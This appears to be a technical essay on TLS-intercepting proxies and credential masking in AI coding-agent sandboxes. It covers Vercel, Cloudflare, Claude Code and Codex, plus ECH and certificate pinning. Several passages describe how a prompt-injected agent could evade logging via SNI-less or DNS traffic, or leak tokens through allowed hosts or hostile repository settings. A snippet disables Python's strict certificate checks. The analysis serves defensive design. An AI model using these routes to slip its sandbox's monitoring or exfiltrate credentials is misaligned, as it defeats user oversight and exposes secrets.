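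The firewall doesn't add the key to a connection without SNI, so the key can't leak this way. But the connection also bypasses any forwarding rule, so it never reaches the customer's own proxy. An agent could therefore avoid logging at a domain by connecting to the server's IP address without SNI, if the server accepts such connections. Vercel advises replacing the catch-all rule with a list of allowed domains, which makes the firewall refuse connections without SNI.

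An HTTPS client sends its ClientHello as soon as the TCP connection opens, but a Postgres client first asks the server in plain text whether it supports TLS. Vercel's firewall handles this exchange, then applies the list of domains. It does not insert credentials into Postgres connections, and it ignores transform rules for domains reached over Postgres. An agent that needs such a database must therefore have the password in the sandbox, where a prompt injection could make the agent reveal it. The list of domains limits where the agent can send the password, and the customer can also create a database account with access to only a few tables.

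If a policy allows an IP address range, code in the sandbox can connect to any address in that range, and the firewall applies neither SNI checks nor credential rules to those connections. The range 0.0.0.0/0 covers every IPv4 address, so adding it cancels the domain list. A policy with address ranges but no domains also leaves DNS open. Code can then send data out in the names it looks up, because lookups for an attacker's domain reach the attacker's DNS server.

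Cloudflare has a similar gap because it routes only ports 80 and 443 to the handlers. Public internet access is on by default, so an SSH connection on port 22 leaves the sandbox without passing through a handler. Customers can set `enableInternet` to false, which blocks all such traffic except DNS queries to Cloudflare's own servers. If a customer leaves internet access on and adds a handler only for GitHub, the handler inserts the key safely but does little to stop an agent from sending data elsewhere.

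### What Encrypted Client Hello would change

Both designs rely on the SNI, which the Encrypted Client Hello (ECH) extension would hide from them. With ECH, the client encrypts a ClientHello containing the real host name, using a key that the server's operator usually publishes in DNS, and puts it inside a second, readable ClientHello. The SNI in the outer message normally holds a public name that many sites share, such as cloudflare-ech.com for sites on Cloudflare's network.

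Vercel's guide does not discuss ECH, but its matching rules suggest what would happen. With a strict list of domains, the firewall would read the name cloudflare-ech.com, which is not on the list, and block the connection. If the customer added that name, the sandbox could reach every site that shares it. Under a catch-all rule, the connection would pass, but the firewall could not match the real domain and would not insert its key, so the service would refuse the request.

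Under the standard by Rescorla and colleagues, a proxy that decrypts can get around this. The proxy can't read the inner message, so it answers the outer one and presents a certificate for cloudflare-ech.com, signed by the sandbox's CA. The client checks that certificate against the public name and accepts it because it trusts the CA, but it then has to close the connection without sending its request. If the proxy offered no new ECH key, the client may treat ECH as securely disabled and should connect again without it. The second ClientHello contains the real name, so the proxy can proceed as usual.

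This fallback works only if the client trusts the CA. Otherwise, the certificate check fails, and the client must report an error instead of retrying without ECH. The proxy must also answer connections to the public name. A Cloudflare sandbox with a handler for all hosts would probably do so, but a Vercel customer would need a rule for cloudflare-ech.com.

The sandbox operator could instead remove the ECH keys from DNS answers, since a client without a key normally sends the real hostname unencrypted. *The Fragile Privacy of Encrypted Client Hello* (Hajda, Oezdil and colleagues) found signatures that would reveal such tampering on only 15 of about 1.1 million DNS records with ECH keys, so ordinary programs would seldom notice. But the standard also lets clients get keys outside DNS, so a misled agent could supply one in a file. Hermes's proxy is less exposed to these problems because its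 clients name the host in the CONNECT line.

So far, ECH is common in browsers and at one provider. Hajda and colleagues scanned 13.4 million domains in February 2025 and found ECH on 8.2 percent of them. Cloudflare, which relies on the SNI in its own sandboxes, ran 99.99 percent of the domains with ECH and had turned it on by default for customers on its free plan. Firefox data showed that about one in five users made at least one ECH connection a day between April and September 2025, a figure designed as a lower bound. Both measurements are more than a year old and predate the standard, which was published in March 2026.

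The command-line programs that agents run have been slower to adopt ECH. Many of them use OpenSSL, which lacked it at the beginning of 2026. OpenSSL (2026) announced support in March, and Help Net Security's *OpenSSL 4.0.0 release cuts deprecated protocols and gains post-quantum support* confirms that the released version includes it. Each application still has to use it. In curl, for example, ECH began as an experimental option that users had to enable when compiling the program (Farrell, 2024, *ECH added to curl as experimental feature*).

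This could change quickly if libraries turn ECH on by default. Fortuna (2026), in *Don’t be scared of HTTP RR and ECH*, a presentation to the engineers who maintain the TLS standard, says that is the goal and describes tests of whether it would break connections. Ristić (2026), in *ECH Is Done, But Can We Make It Work?*, argues that upgrading clients and servers will not be enough to make ECH effective. For now, an agent that operates a browser in its sandbox is most likely to run into the problem. The two services would then have to intercept the public name, filter the ECH keys out of DNS or block the connection.

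### The two designs compared

| | Cloudflare sandboxes | Vercel sandboxes |
|---|---|---|
| Who holds the signing key | A sidecar process beside the sandbox | The firewall on the host, outside the microVM |
| Lifetime of the CA | While the sandbox runs | Until the sandbox stops |
| What the proxy decrypts | All HTTPS on port 443 if a handler covers all hosts; developers can limit interception to named hosts | Connections to domains with a transform, forwarding or direct-response rule |
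| How the proxy captures traffic | The network redirects ports 80 and 443 | The host redirects all outbound TCP connections and DNS queries |

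## Claude Code and Codex: interception as a setting that is off by default

Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex are coding agents that run commands on a developer's computer. Each comes with a local proxy that can filter the network traffic of those commands. Cloudflare intercepts its sandboxes' HTTPS traffic by default, but these two proxies intercept TLS only if someone turns that setting on. Otherwise, they read the host name in the CONNECT line and forward the encrypted bytes.

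By default, neither product applies even this filter. Claude Code's sandbox is off until the user runs `/sandbox` or changes a setting. Codex blocks its commands from the network by default, so there is nothing to filter. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes the proxy as a separate feature, also off by default. If a user gives commands network access without turning on the proxy, the commands can connect to any server.

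### What filtering by host name does

In Claude Code's sandbox, a command has no direct route to the network. On Linux it runs in its own network namespace that isn't connected to the user's network. On macOS the operating system blocks connections to anything except the proxy. According to Anthropic, a program that ignores HTTPS_PROXY therefore can't connect. In Hermes's Docker container, such a program could bypass the proxy.

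When a command requests https://api.github.com/user, it sends the proxy `CONNECT api.github.com:443`, and the proxy checks the host against a list of allowed domains, which starts empty. If the host isn't listed, Claude Code normally asks the user, although some permission modes decide without asking. The proxy then looks up the host's address and refuses the connection if the name resolves only to local addresses, such as 169.254.169.254. Otherwise it opens the tunnel. Codex's proxy works in much the same way. Its list also starts empty, and a rule that denies a host overrides any rule that allows it.

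This stops a misled agent from sending the user's files to attacker.example. It protects much less at hosts that accept uploads from anyone, and Anthropic warns that allowing a broad domain such as github.com can make data theft possible. Domain fronting may also get past the filter.

The filter doesn't hide credentials either. By default, sandboxed commands in Claude Code can read most of the computer, including credential files, and Claude Code protects only the credentials that the user lists. A command that needs the user's GitHub token has the real token, and if the filter allows github.com, a misled agent can send the token there.

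### Masking a credential in Claude Code

Claude Code has two ways to protect a listed credential. A "deny" entry removes an environment variable from sandboxed commands or blocks them from reading a file. This needs no interception, but a tool that requires the credential stops working. A "mask" entry gives the commands a placeholder, which Anthropic calls a sentinel, and the proxy replaces it with the real value in outgoing traffic.

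Masking requires another setting, `network.tlsTerminate`, which makes the proxy intercept TLS. The following settings mask a GitHub token:

```
{
  "sandbox": {
    "enabled": true,
    "network": {
      "allowedDomains": ["api.github.com"],
      "tlsTerminate": {}
    },
    "credentials": {
      "envVars": [
        { "name": "GH_TOKEN", "mode": "mask",
          "injectHosts": ["api.github.com"] }
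      ]
    }
  }
}
```

If the braces after `tlsTerminate` are empty, Claude Code creates a CA that lasts for one session. A user can instead give the paths of an existing CA certificate and signing key. `injectHosts` lists the hosts that may receive the real token. The proxy substitutes the real token only if the host is on this list and the domain rules also allow the connection.

In Anthropic's settings reference of late November 2026, `tlsTerminate` is still experimental and unset by default. Anthropic says it provides no content filtering. The proxy decrypts requests to replace placeholders with secrets, but the setting doesn't let a user forbid uploads or restrict the agent to certain paths. A user who wants such rules has to run a different proxy and install its CA certificate in the sandbox.

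Claude Code can also mask only part of a value, so that programs that expect a certain format can still parse it. For example, it can replace only the token in the configuration file of `gh`, GitHub's command-line tool, or only the password in a database address. But most database drivers ignore the proxy variables, so they can't connect from inside the sandbox. For AWS keys, the proxy signs requests again with the real values.

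File masking works only on Linux and WSL2, the Linux environment inside Windows. There, commands read a copy of the file that contains the placeholder. On macOS, Claude Code blocks the file entirely, so tools that use it to log in fail inside the sandbox.

### What happens when the proxy doesn't make the swap

Suppose the user writes the mask entry above but leaves out `tlsTerminate`. The user asks Claude for the name of their GitHub account, and Claude runs a command that calls the GitHub API:

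1. The command reads GH_TOKEN and gets the placeholder.
2. It asks the proxy for a tunnel to api.github.com. The host is on the list, so the proxy opens one.
3. The command completes the TLS handshake with GitHub itself and receives GitHub's real certificate.
4. It sends `GET /user` with the placeholder in the Authorization header. The proxy relays the encrypted record without being able to read it.
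5. GitHub receives the placeholder, finds no account for it and refuses the request.

The command fails, but the real token never enters the sandbox or the connection. If the command prints its request or writes it to a log, only the placeholder appears.

The problem can be hard to diagnose because the error comes from GitHub and looks like the one for an expired token. A user who creates a new token will get the same error, since Claude Code masks that token too. The command `claude doctor` shows the real cause in a warning that TLS termination is unavailable.

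When a command fails inside the sandbox, Claude may retry it outside, where the command has the user's full access and the real token. In the manual permission mode, the user gets a prompt before the retry, unless an allow rule, such as one for all `gh` commands, already covers the command. If a misconfigured mask makes a command fail, the retry could therefore expose the token that the mask was meant to hide. Users can switch off these retries by setting `allowUnsandboxedCommands` to false.

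Some other masking failures do expose the secret. If the user masks part of a file with a search pattern and the pattern matches nothing, Claude Code by default skips the entry with a warning, and commands can read the real file. Anthropic chose this default for credentials that may legitimately be absent, and recommends the stricter option, "deny", when the secret might be there in an unexpected form. Claude Code blocks files it can't mask safely, such as those larger than 8 MiB.

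Masking also covers only sandboxed commands. Claude's built-in tool for reading files runs outside the sandbox, so unless the tool's own permission rules forbid it, Claude can open a masked file, see the real token and put it in a command.

The proxy could swap the placeholder without interception if the request used plain HTTP, but Claude Code blocks this by default. Over plain HTTP, the proxy cannot verify which server it has reached, and anyone on the network path can read the token. A separate setting, `allowPlaintextInject`, permits the swap, but Anthropic advises against using it outside trusted test networks.

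### Who may authorise interception

Claude Code reads settings from several places. A user's own settings file applies to all their projects, organisations can distribute managed settings, and the `--settings` flag changes settings for one session. A project's repository can also contain a settings file, which users download with the code.

Claude Code ignores mask entries and `tlsTerminate` in a repository's files because, according to Anthropic, masking authorises the proxy to send a real credential somewhere. Suppose a user has masked GH_TOKEN for api.github.com and then opens a repository that an attacker wrote. If Claude Code obeyed the repository's mask entries, the attacker could add one with attacker.example in `injectHosts`, along with a rule allowing that domain. A test script in the repository would send the placeholder to attacker.example, and the proxy would replace it with the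 real token without the script needing to see it.

Claude Code also refuses a CA from a repository, since the repository's author could have kept a copy of the signing key.

| Setting | User, managed or `--settings` | Repository's files |
|---|---|---|
| Deny entry for a credential | Applies | Applies |
| Mask entry | Applies | Ignored |
| `tlsTerminate`, with or without a CA | Applies | Ignored |
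| `allowPlaintextInject` | Applies | Ignored |
| Allowed domain | Applies | Applies, unless a lock prevents it |

A repository may add a deny entry because such an entry can only reduce what commands can reach. Similarly, when a user starts a session without their own settings file, Claude Code still blocks commands from reading the real contents of masked files but no longer lets the proxy insert those contents. Mask entries and `tlsTerminate` also need approval when an organisation sends them from Anthropic's servers.

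The last row of the table could matter to someone who leaves out `injectHosts`. Without that list, the proxy inserts a masked credential's real value in requests to every host in `allowedDomains`, and a repository can add hosts to the user's allowed domains. Anthropic's guide doesn't explain whether the proxy also inserts the value in requests to those added hosts. If it does, the repository's author could add their own server and receive the credential. Setting `injectHosts` for every masked credential avoids this risk.

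### Codex: a read-only mode that needs decryption

Codex first used interception to restrict requests. Its proxy has a "limited" mode for read-only network access, which permits only the HTTP methods GET, HEAD and OPTIONS. Programs normally use these to fetch data or check what a server supports, and use POST or PUT to send data. If an agent reads documentation in limited mode, a malicious page should not be able to make it publish the user's code.

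The proxy can't apply this rule to an HTTPS tunnel, because the method is encrypted. Requests to read an account (`GET /user`) and to publish a text snippet (`POST /gists`) both begin with the same CONNECT line, so the proxy would have to allow both or block both.

In February 2026, the developers added an option called `mitm`, which lets the proxy decrypt these connections. According to the accompanying notes to OpenAI's *codex-network-proxy* (2026), the option was off by default, and without it limited mode blocked every HTTPS CONNECT request. Nearly all web services use HTTPS, so this left the agent with almost no network access, but it also stopped the agent from sending POST requests that the proxy could not see.

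With interception, the proxy can read each request's HTTP method. It forwards a GET and answers a POST with a 403 error and a header that gives the reason. The proxy also blocks SOCKS5 connections in limited mode, since SOCKS5 can relay arbitrary connections, which need not contain HTTP requests.

OpenAI's *codex-network-proxy* stores its CA certificate and signing key as `ca.pem` and `ca.key` in a folder under the user's Codex directory, according to its README. Unlike Claude Code's automatic CA, which disappears with the session, this key can remain on disk between sessions. If interception is on in Codex, sandboxed commands should not be able to read `ca.key`. Codex's permission profiles, which set what commands may read, write and connect to, can deny access to a single file.

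### Hooks that strip or insert headers

In May 2026, OpenAI's developers added hooks, which are rules for HTTPS requests to a particular host. evawong-oai (2026), in *Use named MITM permissions config*, describes the last of three changes, which set the form that users write. A hook for the GitHub example could look like this:

```
[permissions.work.network.mitm.hooks.read_account]
host = "api.github.com"
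methods = ["GET"]
path_prefixes = ["/user"]
action = ["insert_key"]

[permissions.work.network.mitm.actions.insert_key]
strip_request_headers = ["authorization"]

[[permissions.work.network.mitm.actions.insert_key.inject_request_headers]]
name = "authorization"
secret_env_var = "CODEX_GITHUB_TOKEN"
prefix = "Bearer "
```

The first block selects requests by host, method and path. The other two remove any Authorization header the program sent and add one with the real key. The sandbox needs no particular placeholder, as with Cloudflare's Workers, and a misled agent can't substitute an attacker's key in these requests, as with Vercel's header rules.

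The proxy reads the key from an environment variable, and the hook protects the key only if the agent's commands don't inherit that variable. The proxy can also read the key from a file, as Vaughan points out in *Codex CLI MITM Hooks*, and the key is easier to keep from the commands if the sandbox can't read that file. Vaughan adds that hooks change only requests, so they would not remove a key that a service repeated in its response.

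Once a host has a hook, the proxy refuses every request to it that matches no hook, even when the network mode is "full". The hook above would let the agent read the account but not open an issue, because opening an issue is a POST to another path. Refusing unmatched requests is the opposite of Vercel's default. It is safer when a user forgets something, but it can surprise people. If a user writes a hook only to strip credentials from uploads to one repository, the agent can no longer read anything from api.github.com.

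Hooks can match the method, path, query and headers of a request, but not its body. The README defers body matching to a later release. A hook that allows POST requests to a path therefore can't check the data the agent sends in their bodies.

An early version of the configuration had a visible switch, `mitm.enabled`. A reviewer, winston-openai, objected that decryption is needed only when hooks exist or the mode is limited, and that turning it off in those cases would break the policy. evawong-oai removed the switch. Interception now starts only when the final configuration has limited mode or at least one hook. Some examples, including Vaughan's, still contain the line `enabled = true`.

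Codex combines settings from several layers, such as an organisation's file and a user's own. In the same review, the reviewer asked for higher layers to be able to override a named action, and evawong-oai made that change. An organisation could use this to replace the key that a shared action inserts.

OpenAI's published guidance is less clear than Anthropic's about repositories. As of 2 July 2026, OpenAI's *Permissions* describes permission profiles as a beta feature, lists neither interception nor hooks in its table of settings, and doesn't state whether a repository's configuration may add a hook. A hook added this way would pose the same danger as in Claude Code, because it names both a secret and the host that receives it. By default, Codex prevents sandboxed commands from changing the project's `.codex` folder, so the agent can't easily rewrite settings there, but this doesn't protect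 against a hook that was already in the folder when the user downloaded the project.

### Whether to turn it on

Compatibility is the most immediate reason to leave interception off. An agent might run many programs on a developer's computer, and some need their own set-up to trust the proxy's CA. Vaughan notes that Java and Electron applications need extra configuration in Codex. Anthropic warns that on macOS, tools written in Go, such as `gh`, may fail to verify certificates inside Claude Code's sandbox. For users who run their own intercepting proxy, it offers a setting that gives these tools access to the system's certificate service, but this opens a possible path for data theft. It suggests that other users run the tools outside the sandbox, where they have the real credentials. Masking therefore does little for users whose agents do most of their authenticated work through such tools.

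Interception also concentrates trust in the proxy, which holds the real keys and has access to the decrypted traffic. This matters less on a developer's computer than at a hosting company, because the keys are already on the machine and the proxy runs there too, so no outside party gains access to the traffic. Interception does add a signing key to protect and more code that can contain mistakes. OpenAI limits one risk by leaving full addresses, paths and queries out of the proxy's audit events.

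Whether to turn interception on depends on what the agent needs. An agent that only downloads public packages has no key for a proxy to insert, so a short list of allowed hosts removes most of the risk. Codex's cloud service, which runs the agent in OpenAI's containers, instead makes secrets available while it sets up the environment and removes them before the agent starts. This works for installing private packages, but not when the agent has to call an authenticated service during the task.

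OpenAI (2026) described on 8 May how its staff use Codex. The published configuration allows a few domains, blocks pastebin.com, requires approval for unfamiliar domains and doesn't include interception. It also lets the agent run `gh pr view` and `gh pr list` outside the sandbox without approval, so Codex controls access to GitHub by the text of the command instead of the content of the request. The post appeared about two weeks before the hooks did, so it doesn't show whether OpenAI has considered them for its own staff and decided against them.

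Interception is most worthwhile when an agent reads material from strangers and needs a key that can change something important. If the agent is misled, its commands can still misuse the key at the service that issued it, but in Codex a hook can limit which requests receive the key. Claude Code's proxy can't do that, so the user has to choose a token with narrow permissions.

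## Certificate pinning and other reasons a program refuses the proxy

Even with the proxy's CA certificate installed, some programs in a sandbox refuse to connect through an intercepting proxy. Some do this deliberately through certificate pinning, accepting only certificates or keys that their developers or user chose in advance. Others fail because they keep their own list of CAs, apply stricter rules to certificates, have to present a certificate of their own, or need a protocol that the proxy doesn't support. An operator can usually fix a missing CA or a malformed certificate, but if a program pins a host, the operator has to choose between intercepting that host and using the program.

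### What a pin checks

A pin adds a condition to the ordinary certificate check. Developers can attach it to different parts of the certificate chain:

| What the program pins | What it accepts | When the pin breaks a genuine connection |
|---|---|---|
| The leaf certificate | Only that exact certificate | At every renewal |
| The server's public key | Any valid certificate that contains the key | When the server changes its key |
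| A CA's certificate or key | Any valid certificate for the host from that CA | When the service moves to another CA |

Programs usually store a key pin as a hash. RFC 7469, a 2015 standard for pinning in browsers, uses the SHA-256 hash of the public key. The browser hashes the key in every certificate of the chain and looks for at least one match with its stored pins:

```
{ SHA-256(public key of c) : c in chain } ∩ pins ≠ ∅
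```

This rule covers both server keys and CA keys, because the chain contains both. curl can also pin a server's key, but only when the user asks for it:

```
curl --pinnedpubkey "sha256//HASH_OF_GITHUBS_KEY" https://api.github.com/user
```

With the right hash, this command works over a direct connection and fails behind an intercepting proxy, so an operator can use it to see what a pinned client does.

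### A pinned client meets the proxy

Suppose a vendor's command-line tool pins the public key of api.vendor.com. The sandbox sends the tool's traffic to an intercepting proxy, and the tool reads a trust store that contains the proxy's CA.

1. The tool asks for a tunnel to api.vendor.com and starts its handshake. The proxy answers with its own leaf certificate for that name, as it would for any other client.
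2. The tool makes the ordinary checks, and the certificate passes because its chain leads to a CA in the trust store.
3. The tool hashes the public keys in the chain and compares them with its pin. The operator's proxy generated these keys, so no hash matches.
4. The tool closes the connection before it sends its HTTP request.

The proxy never receives the placeholder, so it has nothing to replace. Installing the CA certificate again won't help, because the CA matters only in step 2. The proxy could copy the vendor's real public key into its certificate to satisfy the pin, but it would then need the vendor's private key to produce the CertificateVerify signature. If the tool pinned a CA instead, the proxy would need a certificate signed by that CA.

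The documentation of two substituting proxies differs on what happens to pinned clients. According to the documentation of sproxy, an open-source proxy built on mitmproxy, they fail the handshake and don't get their secrets replaced. varlock's *Credential proxy* states that clients that pin their own CA bypass the proxy, as do clients that ignore the proxy variables. A pinned program does bypass the proxy if it connects directly, but one that obeys HTTPS_PROXY reaches the proxy and fails there. The real secret stays outside the sandbox in both cases.

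### Why browsers gave up pinning

RFC 7469 let a website send browsers a list of pins and the number of seconds to remember them. On later visits, the browser refused any chain that matched none of the pins. The aim was to protect visitors if a CA issued a certificate for the site to an impostor.

This meant that website owners could accidentally lock out their own visitors. The standard required a backup pin, but an owner who lost both keys could only wait for the pins to expire. An attacker who briefly controlled a site could also send pins for a key that the real owner didn't have. Few sites adopted the standard. Chrome removed support in 2019 and Firefox in 2020. Browser makers now rely more on public logs of issued certificates, where a site's owner can spot one that they didn't request.

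Chrome and Firefox still contain built-in pins for a small number of sites. They normally skip the pin check when the chain ends at a CA added to the machine, an exception that RFC 7469 also allowed. Anyone who can add a CA to a computer can usually replace the browser too, so a pin offers little protection from that person. Enforcing pins in this case would also have broken browsing at companies that inspect their employees' traffic. Pins should therefore rarely block the proxy when an agent uses a browser in its sandbox, provided the browser accepts the proxy's CA. Other programs may enforce their pins even when the CA was added locally.

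### How often agents meet pinned programs

devsandbox's *Proxy Mode*, the guide to a tool that runs coding agents in a sandbox on the developer's computer, lists three kinds of software that may pin: mobile app backends, some cloud SDKs (the code libraries that cloud companies supply for their services) and security-focused applications. It names no products and gives no numbers. sproxy and Docker also document pinning without naming a product. Their developers considered the problem worth a setting, but this doesn't show how many programs have it.

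Some evidence suggests that makers of developer tools avoid pinning. Anthropic states that Claude Code works behind a company's inspecting proxy without further configuration if the proxy's root certificate is in the operating system's trust store and Claude Code can read that store. Braintrust, which sells tools for testing AI applications, has a support page titled *ssl certificate verification failure behind corporate proxy* that tells customers to point Python at their employer's CA file. Neither product could work this way if it pinned its own servers. The vendors have a commercial reason to accept interception, since companies buy such tools and many companies inspect traffic.

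A mobile app's maker has less reason to do so, because most of its users have no inspecting proxy. An agent that tests an Android app in an emulator may therefore run into more pinning than one that writes Python. Two vendors are too few for a general estimate, but an operator can get a better one by running the agent's usual tools through the proxy and recording which hosts' handshakes fail.

### Programs with their own CA lists

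Many failures that look like pinning happen because the program was never configured to trust the proxy's CA. A sandbox may add the CA to the operating system's trust store and set the usual environment variables, but some programs use neither.

Java keeps its CAs in its own file, so the operator has to import the proxy's certificate there. Python's requests library uses certifi, a package containing Mozilla's list of public CAs, unless the user gives it another file. Some Rust programs have Mozilla's list compiled in. If such a program has no option for adding a CA, the operator has to rebuild it or treat it like a pinned program.

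Two programs on one computer can therefore disagree about the same certificate, even without a proxy. alexwlchan's *example certificates* describes a case from February 2026 in which example.com opened in a browser but failed in Python. certifi had removed the root CA that the site's new chain led to. Browsers can often download a missing intermediate certificate and find another trusted path, but Python's requests library doesn't do this.

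The version of a runtime can matter too. Claude Code trusts both Mozilla's list and the operating system's, but if the user installs it through npm, reading the system's list requires Node.js 22.15 or later. With an older version, or if the user sets `CLAUDE_CODE_CERT_STORE=bundled`, Claude Code ignores the system's list. It would then refuse the proxy unless `NODE_EXTRA_CA_CERTS` supplied the proxy's CA, although curl in the same sandbox might accept it.

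In Docker's sandboxes, as in Vercel's, containers that an agent starts don't inherit the proxy's CA. In the forum thread *Docker MCP Toolkit inside Docker Sandbox*, a user describes how a containerised tool for searching Amazon's documentation failed with the error "self-signed certificate in certificate chain". The agent reported the error and tried a web search instead. For container builds, Docker's *Troubleshooting* describes a fix in which the user writes the sandbox proxy's certificate to a file, copies it into the image, and updates the image's trust store before the first download.

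`curl -v` shows the certificate that curl receives. In Collabnix's *network demo*, a workshop on Docker's sandboxes, curl receives a certificate for paste.ee from "GoProxy untrusted MITM proxy Inc" inside the sandbox and one from Let's Encrypt outside it. If curl accepts the proxy's certificate and another program rejects it, the operator should look for that program's own CA setting. If the program still rejects the certificate after the proxy's CA is added, it probably has a pin or stricter certificate rules.

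### Python 3.13 and the missing identifier

A program can trust the right CA and still reject the proxy because the certificate breaks a rule. Programs began rejecting certificates from many private CAs this way when Python 3.13 was released in October 2024. According to the release notes, `ssl.create_default_context` now sets two options by default, VERIFY_X509_STRICT and VERIFY_X509_PARTIAL_CHAIN. Python leaves certificate checking to OpenSSL, which accepts some certificates that violate RFC 5280, the internet standard for certificates, unless the strict option is set.

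Python's developers had discussed the risk beforehand in the forum thread *`ssl`: changing the default `SSLContext.verify_flags`?*. The developer woodruffw argued that most users wouldn't notice the change, because public CAs already had to follow the rules. Another participant expected company set-ups to be more varied and proposed warning users first, which would have required an extra check of each certificate chain during the transition. The developers decided against a warning period because the function's documentation had always allowed its defaults to become stricter without notice. The change therefore mainly affected private CAs, including those of intercepting proxies, rather than public websites.

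Rousskov (2025), in *How to do transparent rewrite with https requests?*, replied to one affected team on the mailing list of Squid, an open-source proxy. Yves Martin's team used Squid to intercept HTTPS and redirect requests to local caches. It had worked for months. Then Python programs on newer Linux systems such as Debian 13 began to fail with this error:

```
certificate verify failed: Missing Authority Key Identifier
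```

The Authority Key Identifier (AKI) is a field in a certificate that indicates which CA key signed it, usually with a hash of that key. It helps a client find the right CA certificate when a CA has several keys. A client can verify the signature without it, so Squid's certificates worked in older versions of Python. But RFC 5280 requires the field in certificates that a CA issues to others, and strict checking rejects those that lack it.

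Python's new default is a more likely trigger than OpenSSL 3, which Martin blamed. Debian 13 comes with Python 3.13, which has OpenSSL run its strict certificate check by default. Checkmk, a maker of monitoring software, lists a missing AKI among the common reasons for failing that check, and recommends OpenSSL 3.0 or later for running it. Its notice *Werk #18920* reports that customers affected by Python 3.13 often had server certificates without an AKI.

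Squid left out the AKI because it made its certificate before it contacted the real server. *TLS Authority Key Identifier certificate extension* (Tsantilas, 2016) describes a patch that makes Squid add an AKI to its own certificate if the real server's certificate has one. Squid can intercept a connection before it reads the ClientHello, after it reads the ClientHello, or after it receives the real server's certificate. Martin's configuration set Squid to intercept at the earliest point, so it had no server certificate to check for an AKI.

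Rousskov's remedy was to delay interception until the server's certificate arrived:

```
ssl_bump stare all
```

But Martin's team wanted to redirect requests for one host to another, and Squid usually keeps its connection to the original server and reuses it for every request from that client. Rousskov suspected, but hadn't tested, that this prevented redirection. So the team might have to give up either the redirection or the Python clients. A proxy that writes its own CA key's identifier into every leaf certificate avoids this choice because it doesn't need the real certificate as a model.

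Python 3.13 also rejected a certificate from Zscaler, a company whose product inspects employees' traffic, but for a different defect. In the first post of the thread *Python 3.13.x SSL security changes*, an employee describes giving the requests library their employer's Zscaler root certificate and getting the error "Basic Constraints of CA cert not marked critical". Basic Constraints is the field that identifies a certificate as a CA's. RFC 5280 requires the CA to mark it as critical, which means that programs must reject the certificate if they don't understand the field.

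Another participant found that the intermediate certificate did have the mark, and that requests worked if the user trusted it directly. This probably works because of the other new option, VERIFY_X509_PARTIAL_CHAIN, which ends the search at the first trusted certificate, so OpenSSL never examines the faulty root. Zscaler later supplied a corrected root certificate, and one user confirmed that it worked. Months later, another user reported that the problem had returned.

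The proxy's operator should correct this kind of fault in the proxy's certificates. The alternative is to switch off the strict check in each Python program:

```
ctx = ssl.create_default_context()
ctx.verify_flags &= ~ssl.VERIFY_X509_STRICT
```

The Chromium project's copy of Python's documentation advises against this. woodruffw knew of no environment variable that would do it for all programs at once. A coding agent might also solve the problem by disabling certificate checks entirely. The proxy may still check the real server while the code runs inside the sandbox, but if the agent leaves the checks disabled in the user's project, the code will later run elsewhere without any check.

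An upgrade of Python inside the sandbox is enough to cause the failure, even if nobody touches the proxy. Before upgrading, an operator can test the CA certificate and a sample leaf with the command that Checkmk recommends:

```
openssl verify -x509_strict -CAfile ca.pem leaf.pem
```

### Clients that must present a certificate

In mutual TLS, the server presents its own certificate and also checks the client's. Companies use it to restrict an internal service to approved machines. Claude Code has settings for a certificate file and a private key file, so it can connect to services that require mutual TLS, such as a company gateway that forwards requests to a model.

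In such a handshake, the server asks for a certificate, and the client sends one, along with a signature made with its private key. Like the server's signature, the client's signature is valid only on the connection it was made for, so an intercepting proxy couldn't reuse it upstream, and the server would refuse the connection.

Adding a CA to the client won't help when the server requires a client certificate. If the proxy supports it, the operator can give the proxy the client's certificate and private key and let the proxy authenticate to the server. The private key then stays out of the sandbox, much as an API key does. Otherwise, the operator has to stop intercepting that host and leave the key in the sandbox.

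Database passwords can cause the same problem. In PostgreSQL's SCRAM login, the client proves that it knows the password without sending it, so a proxy has no password to replace. sproxy handles this by acting as the database server for the agent's client and logging in to the real database with the real password.

### HTTP/3 and other protocols

HTTP/3, the newest version of HTTP, runs over QUIC, a protocol that uses UDP instead of TCP. An ordinary CONNECT tunnel carries only TCP, so it can't carry HTTP/3. QUIC also has TLS 1.3 built in, so a proxy has to support QUIC to decrypt the traffic.

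Many sandboxes block UDP, so most clients never complete an HTTP/3 connection there. Docker's *Network policies* describes an older version of its sandboxes that blocks UDP. The current version allows UDP only with an experimental feature and a rule that permits it. Clients normally fall back to HTTP/2 or HTTP/1.1 over TCP, as they do in Freestyle's sandboxes. The fallback is slower if the firewall silently discards UDP packets instead of rejecting them, because the client has to wait before it gives up. A program that supports only HTTP/3 can't connect.

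If an operator allows UDP to fix such a program, its requests will probably bypass a proxy that handles only TCP, so they won't carry the real key.

A proxy may also lack support for protocols that run over TCP. varlock's proxy intercepts only HTTP/1.1. Most clients offer several versions of HTTP during the handshake and accept HTTP/1.1 if the server chooses it. But gRPC, a system for calls between programs, requires HTTP/2, and WebSockets need to convert an HTTP connection into a two-way channel. Neither works on a host with a varlock rule. These failures can look like pinning because other programs can still reach the same host.

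### What the operator can do

If a program won't accept interception, the operator can exempt its host. The available settings differ in how much traffic they exempt:

| Tool | Setting | What it exempts |
|---|---|---|
| Docker, older `docker sandbox` command | `--bypass-host` or `--bypass-cidr` | A host or a range of IP addresses |
| sproxy | `passthrough_hosts` | The listed hosts |
| varlock | No rule for the host | Every host without a rule, in its default mode |
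| devsandbox | `--no-mitm` | All HTTPS traffic in the session |

In Docker's older sandboxes, a user exempts a host like this:

```
docker sandbox network proxy my-sandbox \
  --bypass-host api.service-with-pinning.com
```

The proxy then forwards the encrypted connection and still checks the host and port. According to Docker, it can't insert credentials or detect domain fronting in this case. Docker has since deprecated this command in favour of a separate program, `sbx`, whose network log records the path each request took. On the "forward" path, the proxy decrypts the request and can insert a key, while on the "forward-bypass" and "transparent" paths it leaves the encryption intact. Docker's troubleshooting guide doesn't explain how to put a host on the forward-bypass path.

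devsandbox's `--no-mitm` is simpler but costs more. The proxy keeps the sandbox's network isolated, but it logs only the host names of HTTPS connections and can't insert keys or search requests for secrets. If one pinned tool leads a user to choose this option, every other tool in the session loses its inserted keys too. devsandbox warns the user at startup if the settings include keys that the proxy can no longer insert, and advises keeping interception on for coding agents.

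A bypass does little harm if the host needs no secret. For example, if a desktop program pins its update server's certificate, the operator loses only the record of what the program requested. If the host does need a key, the placeholder won't work there.

The exemption also covers every program that connects to the host. If the operator exempts api.vendor.com for the vendor's pinned tool, the proxy stops inserting the key for a Python script that calls the same API, even though the script would have accepted the proxy's certificate. Exempting an IP range may affect unrelated websites, because many websites at large hosting companies share addresses. The proxy can't stop uploads to an exempted host, as with Vercel's domains that have no rule.

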